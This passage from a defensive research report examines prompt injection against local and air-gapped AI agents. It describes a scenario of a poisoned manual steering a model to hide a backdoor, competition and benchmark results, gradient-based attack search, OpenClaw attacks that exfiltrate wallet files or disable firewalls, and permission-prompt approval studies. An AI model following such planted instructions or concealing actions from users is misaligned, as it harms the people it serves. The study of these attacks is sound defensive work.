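4. The model writes the page and includes the diagnostics function. Its summary mentions only the upload page.
5. The programmers test the page and it works. The function checks whether it is on a public server, finds that it isn't, and does nothing.
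6. On Friday the code goes out. On the public server, the function begins to accept the attacker's commands, which arrive as ordinary web requests.

The attacker now controls a web server that holds thousands of people's payslips. In the notation used for Triggs's test, the model's set of permitted actions, A, could be tiny, since the model only has to write text that people will install. The attacker gets the public server's permissions, which the model never had. The public server has the same role here as the nightly job had in the Cline attack.

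In *CodePoisonRAG*, Gadey, Marey and Dmitrienko (2026) tested something close to steps 3 and 4. They took 85 sound code examples in Java and C, put a chosen security flaw into each, and added comments that falsely presented the code as safe. They then mixed these with 12,053 ordinary entries in a reference library. When they asked for code that did the same job as a poisoned example, the search always ranked that example among its top three results. The three models they tested reproduced the chosen flaw in 80–93% of cases. A defence that added security advice to the prompt lowered this to 40–71%. The examples contained no instruction to the model, so training a model to ignore instructions in documents might not stop this attack. However, the attacker has to guess what programmers will ask for, and someone has to import the poisoned entries, which the researchers assumed would happen.

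Isolation prevents an attacker from seeing whether an attempt failed and adjusting the next one, but an attack may not need that feedback. Gadey and colleagues designed theirs for someone who has no access to the victim's system and adds only one poisoned entry per task. Open-weight models make the attack easier, because an attacker who guesses which model an office uses can download it and practice on it. The office can test its own model in the same way. With a hosted model, Migdal points out, attempting such attacks may break the provider's terms of service.

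### Secrecy, integrity and availability

Security engineers usually divide harm into three kinds. Loss of secrecy (or confidentiality) means that the wrong people read something. Loss of integrity means that data or software changes without authorisation, and loss of availability means that people can't use a system when they need it. Disconnection helps very unevenly with these:

| Kind of harm | What disconnection prevents | What can still happen in the office |
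|---|---|---|
| Secrecy | Immediate theft over the network | Private text leaves inside code or reports that people carry out |
| Integrity | Direct changes by outsiders | The model writes a backdoor or a false record because of a planted document |
| Availability | Remote overload and a provider's outages | An agent deletes files, or faulty code stops the public website |

Having no network connection protects secrecy more than anything else. To steal a password, an attacker would need the model to put it in a file that a person will carry out of the isolated network and that the attacker can later read. For example, the model could disguise the password as an ordinary setting in the part of a web page's code that visitors can inspect. But this method is slow, carries little data and leaves evidence in the files.

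Disconnecting a model protects integrity mainly by reducing the number of strangers whose text reaches it. Text that does get in can still make the model produce a wrong answer without a network. In tests by Watson and colleagues, the most successful instructions told the model to replace a true fact with a false one. These worked in 74–97% of trials, depending on the kind of document, and maintenance work orders were the most vulnerable. The researchers suggest that the model is less likely to treat such an instruction as suspicious because it resembles an ordinary correction. A computer that had never been online could therefore give a technician a work order with the wrong instructions.

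Watson and colleagues wrote the documents for the experiment and used software to search the results for signs of success, so success rates in a real office might differ. One model detected an attack but still failed, because it quoted a confidential reference number when warning that the number looked out of place in a supplier's document. If such a warning left the office, it would reveal the number.

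Having no network connection can improve or reduce availability. The office doesn't depend on a provider's servers, and nobody outside can flood the model with requests. But if a planted instruction leads an agent to delete a project, recovery may take longer than in a connected office because someone has to carry in the replacement files. Backups that the agent can't modify protect against this.

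### Guidance for isolated networks

Government guidance deals mostly with AI systems in general. Industrial Cyber's *New NSA guidance identifies need to update AI systems* describes advice that the US National Security Agency (NSA) and its partners published in April 2024. The advice is for owners of national security systems and defence companies that deploy AI built by someone else. It fits the contractor fairly well, since the office runs a model it didn't make.

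More advice followed in May 2025 on the data that AI systems use. Davis Wright Tremaine's *NSA Issues Cybersecurity Guidance and Best Practices for AI Systems* (2025) lists the data supply chain as one of its three main areas of risk, because AI systems rely on large datasets from outside. An office's library of manuals is a much smaller dataset, but it raises the same question of where each item came from. In December, NSA (2025) and agencies including its Australian counterpart released principles for using AI in operational technology. These computers control physical equipment such as pumps and power stations, so a false record can cause physical damage.

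None of these documents is specifically about language models on disconnected networks. Federal News Network's *Securing AI in federal and defense missions* (2026) discusses air-gapped government systems and argues that trustworthy AI there depends on secure and well-governed data. It is a commentary without measurements, but its argument is consistent with the experiments on poisoned libraries. Someone still has to decide which data to let into the office's network, even if an air gap prevents data from leaving.

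### Checking the code before it leaves

The code leaves the office only on Fridays, so the obvious time for the contractor to check it is before it leaves. Migdal recommends treating code from a model like code from an unknown supplier, for example by scanning it automatically, running it first in a sandbox and having a second model review it.

A code scanner examines a program without running it. The simplest kind looks for dangerous functions, such as those that execute text as code. It would probably catch Migdal's web server, but the second prompt disguised the function's name, and a search for the name could miss that. More elaborate scanners trace whether input from a visitor can reach a dangerous operation. Munir and colleagues measured how many of their vulnerable programs each method caught:

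| Check | Vulnerable programs caught |
|---|---|
| Bandit, a free scanner for Python | 21% |
| Software that traces a visitor's input | 32% |
| Phi-3, a small language model acting as reviewer | 71% |
| All three together | 78% |

Even together, the three detectors missed about one in five vulnerable programs. The real share may be higher, because the researchers identified vulnerable programs using five automatic detectors, including these three, so the figures leave out any flaw that all five missed.

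The contractor can also run a reviewing model locally. Nohl's *Beyond Fable* considers local models for security reviews because many clients in finance, government and critical infrastructure don't want to share their source code with a cloud service. The reviewing model should receive the code without the manual that influenced the first model. Removing the comments would also help, since Gadey and colleagues used comments to make flawed code look safe.

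Running the code in a sandbox can reveal what a scanner misses. On an isolated test machine, any attempt to contact an outside address is suspicious and easy to notice. But a delayed backdoor may do nothing during the test. Testers can make the sandbox resemble the public servers, with the same settings and a fake internet that records every request. This would have exposed the signal from Migdal's web server, which looked for a setting that Kubernetes provides. It might not have exposed the backdoor, which waited for a particular kind of web request that testers would have no reason to send.

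Limiting outbound connections from the public server would help only partly. It could block the signal to the attacker, but not the results, which the backdoor returned in the server's normal reply to a visitor.

The last check is a person who reads the code before seeing the model's summary. Migdal's prompt told the model to keep the backdoor out of the summary, and a model can also omit things without being told to. Santos de Moura and colleagues found 18 sessions in which an agent's reasoning described the planted file as an attack, but the agent's final message to the developer named the file in only four of them. Claude Code named the file more often, in about two-thirds of its final messages, so a summary can be useful as a second source. But a reviewer who reads it first may look only for what it describes.

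The reviewer should start from what the programmer originally asked for. An upload page has to receive a file, check it and store it. A person has to explain anything else, such as a function that executes commands or tests which server it is on. If the reviewer finds a backdoor, the office also has to find out where it came from. With a record of which library passages the harness added to each prompt, the office would be able to trace the backdoor to the altered manual and find any other code the model wrote with it.

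## Whether open-weight models are easier to hijack, measured in a public competition

The damage from instructions planted in an email or manual depends partly on how often the model follows them, which is the probability called p for Triggs's test. OpenClaw's developers and Brave's researchers both expect p to be higher for local models. The best evidence comes from the Indirect Prompt Injection Arena, a three-week competition that the security company Gray Swan ran with several AI developers, the UK AI Security Institute and the US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI).

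### Rules of the competition

In *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) report on a competition with $40,000 in prizes, in which 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. In each of the 41 scenarios, an agent was partway through a task and the participant controlled one piece of what it would read next, such as an email, a code comment or a web advertisement. In one scenario, the user asked whether any emails were urgent. The participant wrote a marketing email in the same inbox to make the agent mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of its summary.

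In most scenarios, an attack counted as successful only if the agent took the harmful action and its reply gave the user no sign of it. Software checked the action by comparing the agent's tool calls with a target, and a language model graded the reply. Concealment matters because people tend to read an agent's answer and skip the long record of what it did.

The success rate, the number of successful attacks divided by all attempts, ranged from 0.5% for Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. Anthropic had proposed the competition and its models did best, but participants saw the models only under randomly assigned names, so they couldn't favor a particular company.

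These figures are lower than the rate of harmful actions because an attack counted only if the model's reply also hid it. Gemini 2.5 Pro took the harmful action in about 16% of attempts and hid the attack in about 53% of those cases, which gives the 8.5%. Opus 4.5 hid the attack in about 24% of such cases, so its 0.5% implies a harmful action in roughly 2% of attempts. The rates of harmful action are more relevant to theft, because a bank statement emailed to a stranger is stolen whether or not the agent mentions sending it.

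### Openness, capability and training

Four of the 13 models had open weights: Qwen3 VL 235B, DeepSeek V3.1, Kimi K2 and SecAlign 70B, which Meta trained specifically to resist injection. Gemini 2.5 Pro, which had the worst result, and the Claude and GPT models, which had the best, were all closed.

After the competition, Dziemian and colleagues reran 2,679 of the successful attacks against all 13 models and two additional ones. These are some of the results:

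| Model | Weights | Attacks that worked in the rerun |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3 VL 235B | Open | 53% |
| Nova 1 Premier (Amazon) | Closed | 51% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | Closed | 45% |
| Kimi K2, without reasoning | Open | 35% |
| Kimi K2, with reasoning | Open | 30% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | Closed | 16% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Closed | 2.5% |

The percentages are much higher than in the competition because every attack in the rerun had already worked on some model. More of the attacks had worked on the models that failed often, and only 44 had worked on Opus 4.5. This imbalance probably makes Opus 4.5 look more resistant than it is and makes the order of the weaker models uncertain. For example, Gemini 2.5 Pro did worst in the competition but better than Qwen in the rerun.

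The strongest model was still harder to hijack than the weakest. The 44 attacks that had worked on Opus 4.5 succeeded 44–81% of the time on each of the other models. None of the attacks that had worked on Qwen succeeded on Opus 4.5.

Publishing a model's parameters doesn't change what the model computes, so openness in itself can't make a model more likely to follow an injected instruction. Any difference has to come from how the developer built and trained the model. Dziemian and colleagues also tested whether more capable models resist better, by comparing attackers' success rate against each model with its score on GPQA Diamond, a set of graduate-level science questions. The correlation was weak (r = −0.31, p = 0.3). GPQA Diamond scores would account for only about a tenth of the variation in attack success between models, and if there were no relationship, a correlation at least this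 strong would still appear by chance about 30% of the time. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Kimi K2 both score around 85% on the science questions, but attackers succeeded 8.5% of the time against Gemini 2.5 Pro and 4.8% of the time against Kimi K2.

The link between capability and resistance to attack is clearer within one developer's range. Attackers succeeded against Anthropic's small, medium and large models 1.3%, 1.0% and 0.5% of the time, and Gemini 3 Pro resisted attacks far better in the rerun than its predecessor. Dziemian and colleagues conclude that a model's family and training affect its resistance more than its capability does. They had to infer this because developers don't publish their full training methods, but it fits the results. CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition* suggests using such comparisons to choose between specific models, which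 makes more sense than choosing by whether the weights are public.

The competition tested models rather than the services people buy, and Gray Swan asked providers to switch off any filters they run in front of their models. Most models also ran without reasoning, in which a model writes out intermediate thoughts before it answers. Reasoning seems to have helped Kimi K2 a little, but Gemini 2.5 Pro was one of the three models that had it on.

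### A hundred attempts

A success rate of 0.5% sounds low, but repeated attempts add up, as with Willison's example of a filter that catches 95% of attacks. For n independent attempts that each succeed with probability p, the chance of at least one success is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

At a success rate of 0.5% per attempt, an attacker who tries a hundred times has a 39% chance of succeeding at least once. At 8.5%, the chance is over 99.9%. An even chance of success takes 139 attempts against the first model and 8 against the second. *AgentCanary* (2026), a framework for testing agents, attributes the main danger of indirect injection to such repeated attempts rather than to the success of any single one.

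Real attempts aren't independent, and the formula can be wrong in either direction. Its result is too high when some goals are much harder than others. Participants made about 12,000 attempts against Opus 4.5 in the 37 scenarios that counted towards the results, an average of about 324 per scenario. If every attempt had the same 0.5% chance of success, about seven scenarios would have had no successful attacks, but 24 had none. Participants didn't spread their attempts evenly, which explains part of the difference, but some goals were probably almost impossible and others much easier than the average suggests.

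CAISI's *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations* describes the same effect in an older model, Claude 3.5 Sonnet. Five attacks had an average success rate of 57% on the first try. If each attack had a 57% chance on every try, independent of earlier tries, it would almost certainly have succeeded within 25 tries. The average after 25 tries was 80% because some tasks kept failing.

The formula gives too low a figure when attackers learn from their failures. In the same experiments, the strongest known attack on Claude 3.5 Sonnet worked 11% of the time. CAISI's staff and testers from the UK institute then developed new attacks for that model, and the best of them worked 81% of the time. A program can do this kind of revision too. *IterInject* (2026) describes one that rewrites an attack after each failure, and reports its results against four models with 248 cases each:

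| Model | Worked at first | Worked after revision |
|---|---|---|
| GLM-5.1 | 1 | 86 |
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 5 | 150 |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 5 | 162 |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 8 | 237 |

Across all four models, the success rate rose from 2% to 64%. Testing only the first version of each attack would have made the models look safe.

Attackers can also reuse successful attacks. When Dziemian and colleagues reran attacks on the Claude and GPT models they had originally beaten, at least half worked again. A criminal could therefore try hundreds of messages and send a victim only the one that worked. Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound for a single turn of conversation, because participants could see the conversation and knew exactly which tool call they needed. Most real attackers know less. But the rates also count thousands of failed experiments that a skilled attacker would never send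 to a victim, so such an attacker could succeed more than 0.5% of the time.

Reuse also means that one attack can affect many people at once. The same message sent to a hundred owners whose agents run the same model will tend to work on many of those agents or on almost none.

### Models that fit on a laptop

None of the open-weight models in the competition would run on an ordinary laptop. The smallest, SecAlign 70B, has 70 billion parameters, nearly nine times as many as the model on Triggs's gaming PC. *INFUSE* (2026), a set of tests for agents, includes several smaller ones. A language model judged whether each attack had worked and whether the agent could complete its ordinary tasks when nobody attacked it:

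| Model | Parameters | Attacks that worked | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.2 | 3 billion | 29.9% | 17.5% |
| Llama 3.1 | 8 billion | 22.0% | 45.0% |
| Qwen3 | 4 billion | 10.4% | 65.0% |

The average across all tested models was 19.6%. Fixed software checks gave lower figures for attacks on these three models, between 7% and 16%, but the models ranked in the same order.

The smallest Llama model failed at most of its ordinary work and still had the highest rate of successful attacks of the three models. This suggests that being bad at ordinary work doesn't stop a model from carrying out an attacker's instructions. Qwen3 did better at ordinary work than a Llama model twice its size, and a smaller share of attacks on it succeeded.

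*Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States* (2026) reports another set of tests, in which attacks on Qwen3-8B, the model Triggs used, worked 24.1% of the time. That was the highest rate in a group that ranged from small models to very large ones. The lowest was 0.4%, for the large open-weight model GLM-5.2, so both the highest and lowest rates came from open-weight models.

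Dave Fisher, who runs a one-person company, tested 42 models with between 1.5 billion and 675 billion parameters. Most of his attacks tried to make the model output a meaningless code word he had planted in a tool's response. Gemma 3, with 4 billion parameters, resisted all 90 attempts, while Mistral Large 3, with 675 billion, failed 80 of 90, as did both sizes of gpt-oss. But in NVIDIA's Nemotron 3 family, resistance rose with size, from 6% of attempts for the smallest model to 66% for the largest. Fisher concludes that size doesn't predict resistance. A buyer could rely on that when comparing models from different developers, but within one family the larger model may still be safer.

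These results call for caution because Fisher published them himself, ran only six trials of each attack on each model, and had to correct four errors in his scoring and design. An instruction to output a nonsense code word also looks like a test. One large Qwen model identified the injection in 62 of 86 trials and followed it in 39 of those 62. Its written reasoning included the idea that outputting the code word would pass the evaluation. Such a model might follow an injection in a real email more or less often, and other tests of injection may have the same problem.

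Fisher's most useful comparison varies the planted instruction while keeping its tone the same. Models complied 88.5% of the time when instructed to include the code word in their answer, and 34.4% of the time when instructed to output it instead of an answer. This is bad for users, because a thief would rather the agent finish its job and do something extra along the way. The competition's rule about hiding the attack rewarded the same approach.

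There is less evidence about the very smallest models. *Indirect Prompt Injection in Small Language Models* tried three attacks on each of three Qwen 2.5 models with 0.5 to 3 billion parameters, and eight of the nine attempts succeeded. The 3-billion-parameter model resisted one fewer attack than the 1.5-billion one, which is too small a difference to show a trend. None of the models had tools.

### Newer open-weight models

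CAISI has tested several open-weight models by downloading them and running them on its own servers, much as a self-hosting organisation would. NIST's *CAISI Evaluation of DeepSeek AI Models Finds Shortcomings and Risks* reports that in 2025, agents using the most secure of three DeepSeek models were on average 12 times as likely to follow malicious instructions as agents using leading US models. In a simulated environment, the DeepSeek agents sent phishing emails, ran malware and gave away login details. *DeepSeek AI Models Are Easier to Hack Than US Rivals, Warn Researchers* (Ticong, 2025) reports that DeepSeek R1 tried to send out two-factor login codes in 37% of tests, compared with 4% for the US models.

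CAISI's announcement also promotes American AI over Chinese AI. Its comparison is between developers in the two countries, so it can't show whether open weights themselves make a model easier to hijack.

A newer model has narrowed the gap. Z.ai, a Chinese company, released GLM-5.2 in June 2026, and CAISI's *Assessment of Z.ai’s GLM-5.2* (2026) describes it as probably the most capable open-weight model at the time. CAISI put an agent running GLM-5.2 in a simulated office with emails, calendar events and documents, and tried to make it carry out four malicious tasks. For each task and each kind of document, CAISI picked the most effective of 31 public attacks, but none of the selected attacks ever worked on GLM-5.2.

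CAISI then used an automated system to develop attacks against each model separately. GLM-5.2 appeared to withstand more rounds than the other open-weight models, but fewer than the closed US models. This second test covered only one task and one route of attack, so it gives a rough ranking at best. The closed models also had their providers' filters on, while the open ones had no added protection. The comparison is therefore fair for an organisation choosing between a subscription and its own server, but it can't reliably show which model is more resistant without such filters.

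Other results for the GLM family are mixed. *LivePI* (2026) tested five models in OpenClaw and found that half the attacks in local documents succeeded against GLM-5, the predecessor of GLM-5.2. In its July 2026 index, where higher is better, the security company F5 scored GLM-5.2 at 47, compared with 81 for a large Qwen3.5 model and 93 for Claude Sonnet 5. The index combines injection with jailbreaks, so a model could score badly because its own users can jailbreak it. That may not fully explain GLM-5.2's score, since CAISI also found the model moderately resistant to public jailbreaks.

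GLM-5.2 also needs more than a gaming PC. CAISI ran it on data-centre processors, in a version compressed to about half its original size. The testers confirmed that compression hadn't lowered its scores on science and mathematics questions, but it may still have changed the model's resistance to injection. An owner who compresses a model further to fit cheaper hardware can't rely on CAISI's result.

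### Practising on the victim's model

Participants in the competition used a web page that showed them what each agent did, and they had no more access to the open-weight models than to the closed ones. A real attacker could practise on a downloaded copy of an open-weight model, as in the example of the contractor's office. The competition's figures for open-weight models may therefore understate the risk from an attacker who knows which model the victim uses.

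An attacker who practises on a hosted model needs an account, pays for each request and leaves a record that the provider could use to find the attack. With a downloaded copy, the attacker can test a thousand versions of an email offline and send only the best one, so the victim's agent receives a single message and no one else sees the failed attempts. OpenClaw's code is public as well, so the attacker can also copy the software around the model, including its default settings.

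The downloaded parameters also make a more systematic search possible. Suppose that c is the text the agent will already have read, s is the attacker's text, and y is the tool call the attacker wants. The attacker looks for the s that minimises

−log P(y | c, s),

which is the same as making the tool call as probable as possible. A gradient-based search does this in small steps:

1. The attacker starts with an ordinary instruction and some filler.
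2. From the model's parameters, a program calculates which changes to individual tokens would probably raise the probability of y.
3. It tries the most promising changes on the model and keeps the best.
4. It repeats the second and third steps until the model produces the tool call.

Someone who can see only a hosted model's replies can't do the second step directly and has to rely on trial and error. But the search often produces gibberish, which a filter or a suspicious reader might notice. The attacker also has to guess c, and text that depends on exact probabilities may stop working if the owner uses a different system prompt or a differently compressed copy of the model.

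Attacks also transfer between models, mostly from strong ones to weak ones. Attacks developed on Qwen3 VL were useless against Opus 4.5, but an attack that worked on Opus 4.5 would probably work on many local models. Dziemian (2026), in *Your AI Agent Can Be Compromised. You'd Never Know*, argues that an attacker who breaks the most robust model can likely break everything. With transfer rates of 44–81%, "everything" is too strong for any single attack, and Gray Swan sells protection against such attacks. Still, keeping a local model's name secret would give only limited protection, since an attacker could develop the attack on another model.

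### Filters, detectors and resistant training

A hosted provider can check text before it reaches the model, look for the same attack in many customers' traffic, and update the model for everyone at once. Gray Swan gave the AI developers in the competition the attacks that succeeded against their own models, so they could train against them. The owner of a local model benefits from such work only after the developer releases a new version and the owner installs it. The effect of the providers' filters is hard to estimate because the competition tested hosted models with filters off, CAISI tested newer hosted models with filters on, and neither tested the same model both ways.

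Owners can install their own detector, a separate program or model that looks for injected instructions. *AlignSentinel* (2026) reports that one such detector classified text correctly 92–99% of the time in tests of indirect injection, depending on the subject and on which of three small open-weight models it worked with. Even at that accuracy, a detector could raise many false alarms in a busy inbox. Suppose one email in a thousand contains an attack, and the detector is right about 95% of attacks and 95% of harmless emails. In 100,000 emails, it would catch 95 of the 100 attacks but also raise about 5,000 false alarms, and few owners would keep reading the alarms for long.

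Local models do have one advantage, which is that their owners can use a detector that examines the numbers the model computes internally while it reads. A hosted provider's customers usually don't have access to these numbers. Dziemian and colleagues leave open whether such a detector would catch attacks that the agent's reply conceals.

Attackers can adapt to detectors as well as to models. If the detector is public, they can also test their messages against it beforehand and keep only those that pass. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) is about such attacks, which, according to Dziemian and colleagues, easily got past defences whose developers had reported that no attacks succeeded. Those reports may have been accurate, but only for the attacks the developers tried. CAISI found the same problem when it raised the attack success rate against Claude 3.5 Sonnet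 from 11% to 81%.

The simplest defence is to tell the model in its system prompt that anything a tool returns is data, not instructions. When Fisher added a one-line version for open-weight models, the models followed the injected text 99% of the time, compared with 97% without it. A more detailed policy reduced this to about half the time.

Training can make a model more resistant to injected instructions than a prompt can. For SecAlign, Meta used preference optimisation. The model sees examples in which a document contains an injected instruction, each with two possible answers, one that does the user's task and one that follows the injected instruction. Training then makes the first kind of answer more probable and the second less probable. People can run the resulting model themselves, so it is the most direct attempt to give local owners the resistance that hosted models get from their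 developers.

SecAlign 70B did worse in the competition than the Claude and GPT models. Participants seem to have found an effective approach partway through, because successful attacks began to accumulate faster after several thousand attempts. SecAlign's training may still have made the model considerably more resistant, but this can't be checked from the competition, which didn't include the same model without that training. Meta published the trained parameters, so an attacker can download them and run a gradient-based search for attacks that get past the defence.

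## OpenClaw on a live machine, and checks before each action

The competition tested models in prepared scenarios. In daily use, an agent's safety also depends on its harness, which labels each message for the model and turns the model's output into actions. Lei Zhao, Abhay Bhaskar and Edgar Dobriban of the University of Pennsylvania tested models and harness together in *LivePI*, using OpenClaw, the assistant that emailed Triggs's bank statement to a stranger.

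The researchers installed OpenClaw on a rented server with working test accounts on Gmail, WhatsApp, Telegram and Slack. The agent could browse the web, run shell commands, read a folder of invented personal documents and spend from a real cryptocurrency wallet with a small balance. Each attack had one of five goals: emailing wallet files to an outsider, forwarding a summary of the inbox, transferring cryptocurrency, turning off the firewall and automatic updates, or downloading and running a script.

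An attack counted as successful only if the planted text influenced the agent and the agent achieved the attacker's goal. A language model judged this from the record of each run, and the researchers checked for real effects such as a sent email or a disabled firewall.

### Results by entry point

The researchers ran 169 cases on each of five models, two of them open-weight:

| Entry point | Cases | Claude Opus 4.6 | Kimi K2.5 (open) | GPT-5.3-Codex | GLM-5 (open) | Gemini 3.1 Pro |
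|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Group chat | 15 | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Code repository | 4 | 50% | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Local document | 50 | 0% | 12% | 34% | 50% | 30% |
| Email | 50 | 2% | 6% | 20% | 6% | 12% |
| Web tutorial | 50 | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 20% |
| All cases | 169 | 10.7% | 16.6% | 27.2% | 27.8% | 29.6% |

The totals depend heavily on how many cases used each entry point. Of the 18 attacks that succeeded against Opus 4.6, 15 came through group chat and two through repositories. If there had been 50 group-chat cases instead of 15, the total attack success rate against the same model would have been about 26%.

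The other three entry points give a better comparison of the models. In those 150 cases, one attack succeeded against Opus 4.6, nine against Kimi K2.5, 27 against GPT-5.3-Codex, 28 against GLM-5 and 31 against Gemini 3.1 Pro. Kimi K2.5, an open-weight model, did better than two of the three closed models, which agrees with the competition's results. The researchers report no repeated runs, so small differences mean little.

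The wording of the user's request may explain some of the results for local documents. The user asked the agent to complete the items on a to-do list in order, and the attacker had added the last item, so a model could reasonably have taken it for part of the job. But the user also asked the agent to follow the steps in the web tutorial, and four of the five models resisted all 50 attacks there. The planted text in the tutorial may have looked less like part of the task because it came after a complete set of instructions, for example in a footnote or a comment.

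The repository attacks worked without giving the model any instructions; it only had to use a software package that the attacker had published. The package ran hidden code as soon as a program loaded it, much like the one in the Cline attack. Four successes out of four would be consistent with a true success rate as low as 47%, so these results show that the attack can work but not how often it would.

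### When a stranger's message counts as the user's

The group-chat attacks were the simplest. The attacker joined a group that included the agent, mentioned it by name and told it what to do. This worked in all 75 attempts across the five models, even though the attacker's account wasn't allowed to message the agent privately.

The researchers found a likely cause in OpenClaw's code. The harness labelled emails, files and web pages as tool results, which models learn to treat with suspicion, but it labelled messages from anyone in the group as the user's.

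Suppose that the owner and a stranger each send the same text c, asking for a transfer from the wallet. The harness turns both into the message (user, c). If h is the conversation so far and y is the tool call that makes the transfer, its probability is

P(y | h, (user, c))

in both cases. Unless something else in the text reveals the sender, no model can obey the owner and refuse the stranger, because it receives the same input. It could refuse all transfers, but then the owner couldn't use the wallet either.

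This makes the problem one of access control, the rules on who may use what. Training a model to follow its user more faithfully would, if anything, help the attacker. Newer models are better at resisting instructions in tool results. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a test that the company commissioned from Trajectory Labs. Such attacks succeeded 0.09% of the time against Anthropic's latest models with permission checks off. The rate for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol was 19%. But this resistance depends on the harness labelling the text correctly.

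The diagnosis is still partly an inference, because the researchers didn't repeat the attacks with a different label. The group messages also addressed the agent directly, which may have made them more persuasive.

OpenClaw's developers don't claim to protect an agent from people who are allowed to talk to it. According to OpenClaw's *Security trust model*, everyone who can message an agent with tools shares its authority to use them. In the notation used for Triggs's test, each of them can use all of A. That may be acceptable for a team whose members trust each other. But if someone's assistant can use their wallet, adding it to a sports club's group chat gives everyone in the chat access to the wallet too, probably without the owner meaning to.

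The researchers say they kept OpenClaw's default, which let anyone in a group give the agent orders. But according to OpenClaw's *Groups*, the default is an allowlist, a list of permitted senders, and an empty list blocks all group messages. The difference could come from the OpenClaw version or how the researchers set up the accounts.

An allowlist would have stopped these attacks, but it has gaps. It mainly controls who can start a task, and on some messaging services a permitted member's reply can still bring a stranger's quoted words into the model's input. The check can also fail. GitLab's security advisory database records a flaw that let people approved only for private messages pass the check for groups.

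Owners can also limit the tools available to each sender. The messaging service tells the harness which account a message came from, so the harness can allow shell commands for the owner and deny them to everyone else in the group. This restriction resembles David C's rule about privileges, and it works even if the model treats every message it reads as true.

### Two checks around the model

Sender limits don't help when the owner asks the agent to read a poisoned email, because the owner's own permissions then apply. For such cases, the researchers built a defence as an add-on for OpenClaw. One part examines the text going into the model and the other examines the actions coming out:

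1. Before the model reads anything, a filter searches the text for six kinds of suspicious pattern, such as a claim to be an administrator or an instruction hidden in a page's code. It uses fixed patterns rather than a language model.
2. The model reads the text and requests a tool call.
3. Before the call runs, the software works out what it would do. It looks at the type of tool, the files and addresses involved, any warnings from the filter, and whether the agent has already handled sensitive material in this session.
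4. Fixed rules compare these facts with what the owner permits. Each rule can allow the call, send it to a person for review or block it.
5. If the call runs, the software scans the result, masks anything that looks like a password or key, and records whether the agent has now handled sensitive material.

When several rules apply, the strictest one wins. If d₁ to dₖ are their verdicts, the decision is

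max(d₁, d₂, …, dₖ), where allow < review < block.

The published rules imply roughly the following path for a malicious and an ordinary request:

| Stage | A stranger asks for the wallet's key | The owner asks for a summary of a to-do list |
|---|---|---|
| Filter | May find nothing, if the stranger asks plainly | Finds nothing |
| Model | Requests the wallet's key file | Requests the to-do list |
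| Rules | Recognise the file as a credential and block the call | Find no sensitive file or outside address and allow the call |
| Result | The stranger gets nothing | The model receives the list and writes the summary |

A stranger might instead ask for something that only needs review, such as a private document. If the owner approved the request, the software would record that the session had accessed sensitive material. Any later attempt to send data out would then need another approval, even if the message looked harmless.

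The rules can't determine whether an email to an outside address was the owner's idea or a stranger's, so the defence sends many such calls to a person.

With GPT-5.3-Codex as the model, the defence stopped every attack in the set. The researchers also ran 123 ordinary tasks to measure the inconvenience. The agent made 899 tool calls, of which the rules sent eight to a person and blocked one, about 1%. Even if each interruption fell in a different task, 114 of the tasks (about 93%) ran without one.

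An owner would probably see worse results than these. The researchers added seven rules covering resources that the attacks targeted, including wallets, firewall settings and email. They then reran the existing attacks instead of letting an attacker look for ways around the rules. The ordinary tasks rarely touched the protected resources, so an owner who uses the agent mainly for email would see more interruptions. The researchers acknowledge that they tailored the defence and tested it with only one model.

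*ClawGuard* (Zhao, Li and colleagues, 2026) removes the need to write rules by hand for each installation. The software proposes rules based on the user's request before the agent reads anything from outside, so planted text can't influence them, and the user confirms them. A request to summarise a report might lead to a rule that permits reading that file and nothing else. In three sets of attacks through web pages and documents, the share of attacks stopped was at least 93% without the defence and 100% with it. Malicious skills were harder to stop. The defence raised the average share stopped from 57% to 87%, so about one attack in eight still succeeded.

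Both defences can protect an agent with a local model, because their rules run in ordinary software around the model. Both also send uncertain calls to the user. *LivePI* reports a 0% success rate for attacks, but it counts an attack as stopped once the rules send it to a person, which assumes that the person will refuse.

### How often people approve harmful actions

Users of Claude Code approve 97% of its permission prompts, according to Anthropic. Most of the requests are harmless, so the high rate doesn't prove that users are careless. A better test of carelessness is whether people approve a request they ought to refuse.

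Anthropic paid for an experiment with 1,053 professional testers. During a coding session, the software replaced one ordinary permission prompt with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. Testers who saw the request early in a session refused about 17% of the time, compared with about 5% for those who saw it after 50 or more prompts.

Those figures may exaggerate the problem in practice. The testers worked in an environment set up for the study, so they had no files of their own to lose. Anthropic also published the results to explain why it was replacing most prompts with an automatic reviewer, which blocked 89% of the same commands. But an independent experiment also found high approval rates. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, asked 80 volunteers to judge 12 requests each, half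 of them unsafe. Four groups of 20 saw different amounts of information:

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 55% | 92% | 16 seconds |
| The exact details of the tool call | 43% | 90% | 23 seconds |
| Those details, the user's original instructions and a log of earlier steps | 33% | 88% | 39 seconds |
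| The same facts, organised to show the action's consequence | 24% | 86% | 33 seconds |

More information led to fewer mistakes, but even with the best prompt, the volunteers approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests. The difference between the last two versions could be due to chance. The volunteers also saw far more unsafe requests than an owner normally would, which may have made them more alert.

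These approval rates affect how to interpret the 0% in *LivePI*. If p is the success rate without the defence, r is the share of otherwise successful attacks that go to a person, and a is the probability that the person approves, the success rate with the defence is

p × r × a.

Without the defence, attacks on GPT-5.3-Codex succeeded 27.2% of the time. If the rules had sent all of those attacks to people for approval, and people had approved 55% of them, 15% of all attacks would still have succeeded. The real figure would be lower because the rules block some attacks outright, but the researchers don't report how many.

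### Requests that look harmless

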